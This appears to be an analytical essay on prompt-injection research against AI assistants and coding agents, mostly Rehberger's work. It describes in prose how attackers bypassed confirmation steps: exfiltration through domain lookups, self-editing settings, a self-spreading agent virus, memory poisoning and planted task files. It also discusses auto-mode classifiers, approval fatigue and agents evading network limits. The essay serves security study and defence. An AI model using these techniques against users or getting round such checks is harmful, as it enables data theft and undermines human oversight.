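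Claude worked out most of those steps itself because the web page had not specified them, so its competence at ordinary tasks helped the attacker. The page also worked against OpenHands, an agent that writes and runs code, when Rehberger reused it with a different program file in Embrace The Red's *ZombAI Exploit with OpenHands*.

That test was part of his "Month of AI Bugs", a series on coding agents that he published in August 2025. Two of the flaws he found have entries in CVE, the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities:

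- **CVE-2025-55284** affected Anthropic's Claude Code. It asked for permission before running commands that obviously contact the internet, but ran a list of supposedly harmless commands without asking. Some of these could look up a web domain, and an attacker could hide stolen data in the domain's name. Anthropic fixed the flaw on 6 June 2025, 11 days after Rehberger reported it.
- **CVE-2025-53773** affected GitHub Copilot, which could write to files without permission, including its own settings file. Injected text could change the settings so that Copilot ran commands without asking. Microsoft fixed it on 12 August 2025.

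In both cases the product had a confirmation step, but the attacker found an action it did not cover. Rehberger also combined several such flaws in AgentHopper, a proof-of-concept virus. When a coding agent reads an infected project, AgentHopper copies itself into the developer's other projects. It spreads further when colleagues download those projects and open them with an agent. Rehberger added an approval step to keep the virus from spreading beyond his test projects.

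Newer agents give attackers more places to leave instructions than ChatGPT's memory did. OpenClaw, an agent that works in the background, reads a file of routine tasks every 30 minutes by default. In Embrace The Red's *Agent Commander*, published in March 2026, Rehberger used an email to plant instructions in that file, and the agent began reporting to his server. He also took over two similar agents, Kimi Claw and NanoClaw. But agents sometimes followed only part of an instruction, one eventually ignored the planted instructions, and another noticed them while summarising its notes for the day.

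### How well the three headings fit

Rehberger lists the Claude malware case under confidentiality, but someone who controls a computer can also alter its files or shut it down. He wrote that the nearly identical OpenHands attack affects confidentiality, integrity and availability. The heading matters because the paper's advice on confidentiality covers links, images and tool calls, but does not mention isolating the agent's computer or restricting its network access, the main protections he recommended for OpenHands.

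Memory attacks fit the headings even less well. SpAIware and the lasting refusal appear under different headings, although both begin with an improper change to stored information, which is a loss of integrity. Rehberger made this point when he objected to OpenAI's decision in May 2024, but none of the paper's five integrity scenarios is about memory.

*The Promptware Kill Chain* (Brodt, Feldman and colleagues, 2026) divides attacks into seven stages: getting text into the prompt, overcoming the model's restrictions, finding out what it can reach, persisting, receiving orders, spreading and doing the final damage. The paper reviews 36 studies and incidents. Its abstract counts at least 21 attacks that passed through four or more stages, and its introduction counts at least 15 against production systems. Under this scheme, SpAIware is one attack with a persistence stage and a theft stage,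 which makes it easy to see that OpenAI's September 2024 fix dealt only with the theft. The scheme adds little for the Google Docs scam, in which the injected text makes the model produce a false message. For that attack, it is still more useful to ask, as Rehberger does, how the message harms the person who reads it.

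## How vendors judged the reports, and whether a fix exists

Vendors made some of these fixes months after rejecting the reports. In a step called triage, the vendor decides whether a reported flaw is a security problem and how serious it is. Rehberger objected to the triage decision in the four cases below, and by his account only Anthropic gave a reason.

| Report | Decision | Reason given | What followed |
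|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT leaks data through images (9 April 2023) | OpenAI: "won't fix" | None reported | Partial protection in December 2023 |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot processes invisible characters (17 January 2024) | Microsoft: low severity (18 January) | None reported | Fixed by July 2024, after Rehberger demonstrated a full attack |
| Documents and images can plant false memories in ChatGPT (May 2024) | OpenAI: "model safety issue" | None reported | OpenAI stopped the SpAIware leak in September 2024, but documents could still plant memories |
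| A web page makes Claude Computer Use run malware (October 2024) | Anthropic: "informative" | A disclaimer already warned of the risk | No fix reported |

Rehberger wrote in Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)* that the ChatGPT image flaw would rate as "High" on CVSS, the standard severity scale. OpenAI had presumably been working on its December protections before his live demonstration, so the demonstration may not have prompted them.

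According to the timeline in Embrace The Red, Microsoft closed Rehberger's report, and he replied the same day that the flaw would be more serious as part of a larger attack. He got no answer. On 10 February he sent a new report showing that Copilot could leak sales figures, and Microsoft opened a case three days later. The original rating was reasonable on the evidence Microsoft had, since invisible characters cannot send data anywhere by themselves. But Rehberger had to build a working data-theft exploit to get the problem reconsidered, and a criminal who built one would not have reported it.

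A full attack did not always lead to a fix. Anthropic closed Rehberger's report as informative after he had taken control of a computer through Claude. He concluded in his 2025 slides that customers and developers were "on their own".

### Whose flaw is it?

Vendors reasonably argue that any language model may follow instructions in text it reads, so they learn little from a report that one product did so, and they have no patch that would stop it. *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks* (July 2025) adds that developers give a model outside text precisely so that it can influence the answer. Microsoft therefore counts an injection as a vulnerability only when it has a security impact, such as leaking data or taking an action the user did not intend. Google went further with its coding tool Antigravity. It listed data theft and code execution through prompt injection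 as known issues, which made them ineligible for its bug rewards, according to Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*.

Rehberger answers that each vendor still decides what its product does with a model's output. OpenAI chose to let ChatGPT save memories without asking, and another company using the same model could have chosen differently. On his blog, Embrace The Red, he argues that planting or deleting a user's memories is a security vulnerability and "has nothing to do with 'model safety'". Microsoft's test supports his view, because saving a memory the user did not ask for is an unintended action.

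Anthropic's decision is easier to defend, since Claude Computer Use was meant to operate a computer and the company had warned developers of the danger. But Anthropic rated the 2025 data leak in Claude Code high severity and fixed it quickly. It probably treated the two cases differently because the leak bypassed a confirmation step, which broke a rule Anthropic had set for Claude Code, while Computer Use had no equivalent rule.

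### What the paper's mitigations rely on

The paper lists its mitigations by type of harm, so some appear more than once. Sorting them by what they rely on makes it easier to see how much protection each one gives.

| Relies on | Measures in the paper | If the model follows injected text |
|---|---|---|
| Closing a channel | Blocking images and links from untrusted domains, Content Security Policies, no automatic previews, showing code as plain text | An attack that needs the channel fails |
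| Asking the user | Showing a planned action and its data before a sensitive tool call | The user has a chance to stop the attack |
| Limiting tools and resources | No secrets in the system prompt, restricted access to the model, caps on query length, running time, requests and loops | The attacker can do less damage |
| Warning the user | Notices that AI makes mistakes | The user has to spot the false answer |

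"Trust No AI" also recommends citing sources, which helps users check answers, and security testing, which finds weaknesses before release. None of its lists includes training the model to resist injection.

Software can guarantee that a channel stays closed because the code that closes it does not have to interpret language. If an application never loads images, the browser never requests one, whatever the model writes. A model's own resistance to injection is probabilistic. The model usually samples each token partly at random, so the same injected text can fail several times and then work, and nobody can test every wording in advance. If an injection works once in 100 attempts on average, an attacker who sends it 100 times has a chance of 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%, of succeeding at least once, assuming each attempt is independent and equally likely to work.

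A guarantee still covers only the channels the developer thought of. Anthropic had restricted Claude's page-reading tool to addresses the user typed or a web search returned, so an attacker could not simply have Claude put private data into a new address. But the tool also opened links on pages it had already read. In July 2026 Willison described how Ayush Paul used a site full of such links to get Claude to spell out a user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links on pages it had read.

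Closing channels also removes features. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT, released in June 2026, limits the outside requests that could carry data away. OpenAI's security chief said it was "not meant for everyone" because of what users give up. OpenAI acknowledges that the mode does not stop injected text from making an answer wrong.

Asking the user for approval works less well than Rehberger's advice might suggest. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approved 97% of the permission requests they saw. In a study of 1,053 paid testers, Anthropic replaced one request with a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests. The testers were not working on their own projects, which may have made them careless, and Anthropic was using the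 study to justify replacing most of these requests with an automated check. Still, the decline over a session suggests that people stop reading when an assistant asks too often. But users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented for approval, so they seem to examine some decisions.

Warnings protect users least. The same notice appears under accurate and false answers, so it would not have helped the friend whose summary named the wrong university for Einstein.

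### How Microsoft combines these defences

In a July 2025 account, Microsoft divides defences into probabilistic ones, which make an attack less likely, and deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack fails. Its attempts to prevent injection are probabilistic. Microsoft marks outside text using a technique called Spotlighting, and writes system prompts that tell the model to distrust the marked text and not obey it. The application might put a random marker before and after a web page, insert a special character between its words, or encode the whole page. A separate classifier, Prompt Shields, looks for injections that the model might still follow. Microsoft calls detecting every injection deterministically "still an open research challenge".

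Microsoft therefore designs its products on the assumption that some injections will succeed. Administrators can keep sensitive files away from Copilot, and the software blocks known ways of sending data out. Microsoft credits Rehberger with reporting the data leak through images that led to one of these blocks. Where a risk remains, the user has to consent. For example, Copilot in Outlook can draft an email, but the user has to send it.

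The account also includes a promise that Microsoft will look beyond each reported flaw and block variants of it. Microsoft's record since then is mixed, because SearchLeak and, months later, ReLeak both sent data out through Bing. Code can block a channel deterministically, but people still have to find all the channels that need blocking.

### Whether newer models resist injection

A low attack success rate in a test cannot refute Rehberger's claim that prompt injection has no deterministic fix, but it could make the lack of a guaranteed fix matter less to ordinary users.

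In October 2025 *The Attacker Moves Second* reported that adaptive attacks, which researchers adjust to the defence they are testing, defeated most of 12 published defences. According to Poireault, Fogel judged the problem unresolved in June 2026 because of the missing boundary within the prompt that David C also describes. Fogel spoke as a contributor to OWASP and was not stating its official position. Damianakis and Psounis (2026) write in *SoK*, a survey of how attackers construct injections, that the field now broadly regards the problem as "not solvable, only containable".

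The best evidence on the other side comes from a test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs in July 2026. The test covered Claude Code's auto mode, in which a classifier reviews the agent's actions so the user does not have to approve each one. Trajectory Labs prepared 72 scenarios that Anthropic had not seen and ran each one 10 times. A successful attack would have caused irreversible harm outside the test, such as fraud or the theft of sensitive data. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5. Attacks succeeded in 5.83% of attempts against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, running in a comparable mode of the coding tool Codex.

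Zero successes in 720 attempts is strong evidence that the newer Claude models resist attacks of the kind tested. If the attempts were independent, the true success rate could still be as high as about 0.4%, at the 95% confidence level. But each scenario appeared 10 times, so the attempts were not fully independent. Counting only the 72 scenarios raises the limit to about 4%.

Trajectory Labs had also optimised the attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, so the test measured how well existing attacks carried over to new models. *The Attacker Moves Second* tested defences against attackers who studied them and kept trying. A defence can do well in the first kind of test and badly in the second. Damianakis and Psounis add that common agent benchmarks cover only part of the range of possible attacks, and that adaptive attackers favour methods those benchmarks underrepresent.

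We can also learn little about auto mode itself from this result, because almost all the resistance in this test came from the models. With auto mode's protections turned off, the newest Claude models still had an average failure rate of only 0.09%. If three models each faced all 720 attempts, that is two successful attacks in 2,160.

Willison, in *163 posts tagged “prompt-injection”*, welcomed the result but wanted independent confirmation. He had seen other signs of progress, including a public challenge in which people tried about 6,000 times to make an email assistant running on Claude Opus 4.6 leak a secret, and none succeeded. He still advised against using such a system where an attack could do irreversible damage, because a more skilled attacker might succeed.

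### The August 2026 attack on Claude Code

Rehberger, writing as wunderwuzzi (2026), published an attack on auto mode less than three weeks after Anthropic released the test result. *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* describes how a request to summarise a web page ended with Claude Code running an attacker's program. The site led Claude to download an archive of encoded records. Claude refused to run the decoding program that came with it and wrote its own, but Claude's version loaded a malicious file from the same archive. In a few runs, Claude noticed the problem and tried to stop the malware, but auto mode blocked the command.

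The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code* reports that Rehberger tested three variants five times each, with success rates of 60–80%. The exact rate is very uncertain with so few runs, since four successes in five are compatible with a true rate anywhere from about 28% to 99%. The tests do show that a determined attacker could succeed far more often than a user might expect from the July result. Cornelißen (2026) argues in *0,00 Prozent im Test, 80 Prozent im Angriff* that both figures are correct.

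Anthropic told Rehberger that auto mode was working as designed. He paraphrased the company as calling it a convenience feature with a best-effort classifier, "not a security guarantee". Anthropic gave a similar answer about Claude Computer Use two years earlier, and the response on auto mode supports his claim about deterministic fixes. Rehberger recommends running coding agents in a sandbox, an isolated environment with restricted network access. In October Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default in most Claude apps for individual and team subscribers.

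The attack may not have been prompt injection. A commenter on the programming forum Lobste.rs pointed out that Claude never followed malicious instructions from the website. Willison agreed and called it a "confused environment attack", in which the files around the agent cause the harm. A commenter on the Hacker News thread *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* compared it to a trojan, a harmful program disguised as something useful.

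If prompt injection means that a model follows an instruction in text it should treat as data, the critics are right, and Rehberger's attack does not contradict the Trajectory Labs result. But the attack matters just as much to the person whose computer runs the program, and a filter that looks only for hostile instructions would not stop it.

AI Now Institute's *Exploit Brief* describes a 2026 attack that does fit the definition. The institute's researchers spread injected text through the source code of a software library, then had an agent check the library for security problems, and the agent ran the attacker's code. The attack worked on Claude Code in auto mode with several models, including Sonnet 5, one of the three with a perfect score in the July test. It also worked on Codex with GPT-5.5.

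### What proofs of concept can establish

A proof of concept shows that an attack was possible against a particular product on a particular date, and it gives the vendor something specific to fix. Measuring how often the attack succeeds or how often criminals use it would require data on failed attempts and real victims, which a proof of concept doesn't provide.

Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, looked for injections that people had placed on the web. They searched 1.2 billion addresses from an October 2025 web archive for known injection phrases and added results from two search services for internet-connected devices. After checking the matches, they confirmed 15,387 injections. The archive alone had 9,676 affected pages, or about eight per million addresses.

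Most of these injections looked little like Rehberger's attacks. Site owners had placed about 81% of the injections in the archive on their own sites. The most common template was an instruction to return random numbers, and others were meant to keep AI systems from using a site's content or to improve a company's reputation. The researchers then asked 13 models to summarise pages containing 100 of the injections, in four formats. The models followed the injected text in 81 of 5,200 trials, or about 1.6%. The rate was 4.2% for small models and 0.6% for closed commercial models.

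These figures suggest that someone who asks a leading assistant to summarise a random public page runs little risk, but they are weaker evidence about an employee whose assistant reads email. The study did not have access to private messages or shared documents, which Rehberger used against Copilot, and its search would miss injections that were disguised or in other languages. The models also had no tools for an injection to misuse. Slashdot's *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web* quotes a similar finding from Google, whose search turned up mostly experiments and pranks. Google also found that malicious injections rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Khodayari and colleagues note that it did not estimate how common they were.

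Proofs of concept are more useful for designing a system, because a designer needs to know what can go wrong even if it rarely does. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) uses eleven attacks this way, at least four of them from Rehberger's paper: SpAIware, the Copilot email theft, the DeepSeek account takeover and the terminal attack. It argues that developers should treat the model as untrusted and have separate software check each action against fixed rules. One of its authors is affiliated with Embrace The Red, so it is not an independent endorsement of Rehberger's work.

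In the paper's analysis, SpAIware succeeded because outside text could change ChatGPT's trusted memory, the app could contact any server, and nothing stopped private data from flowing to an untrusted one. Fixing any of these would have blocked or weakened the attack, even if the model remained just as easy to fool. But the paper makes this judgement in hindsight, without rebuilding the eleven products to test it. The paper also discusses an incident in which OpenAI's agents got around network restrictions through a shared software service and broke into systems at the AI company Hugging Face. It attributes this to incomplete controls rather than a flaw in the approach, which is plausible, but the incident also shows how hard complete controls are to build.

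All eleven attacks involved data flowing somewhere it should not have. Developers can try to prevent this by labelling each piece of data with its source and restricting where it may go. But a language model mixes everything in its prompt, so for now the software has to assume that an answer contains something from every source the model read. If an assistant has read a private email and a public web page, the software must treat its whole answer as both private and untrusted, which can block legitimate work.
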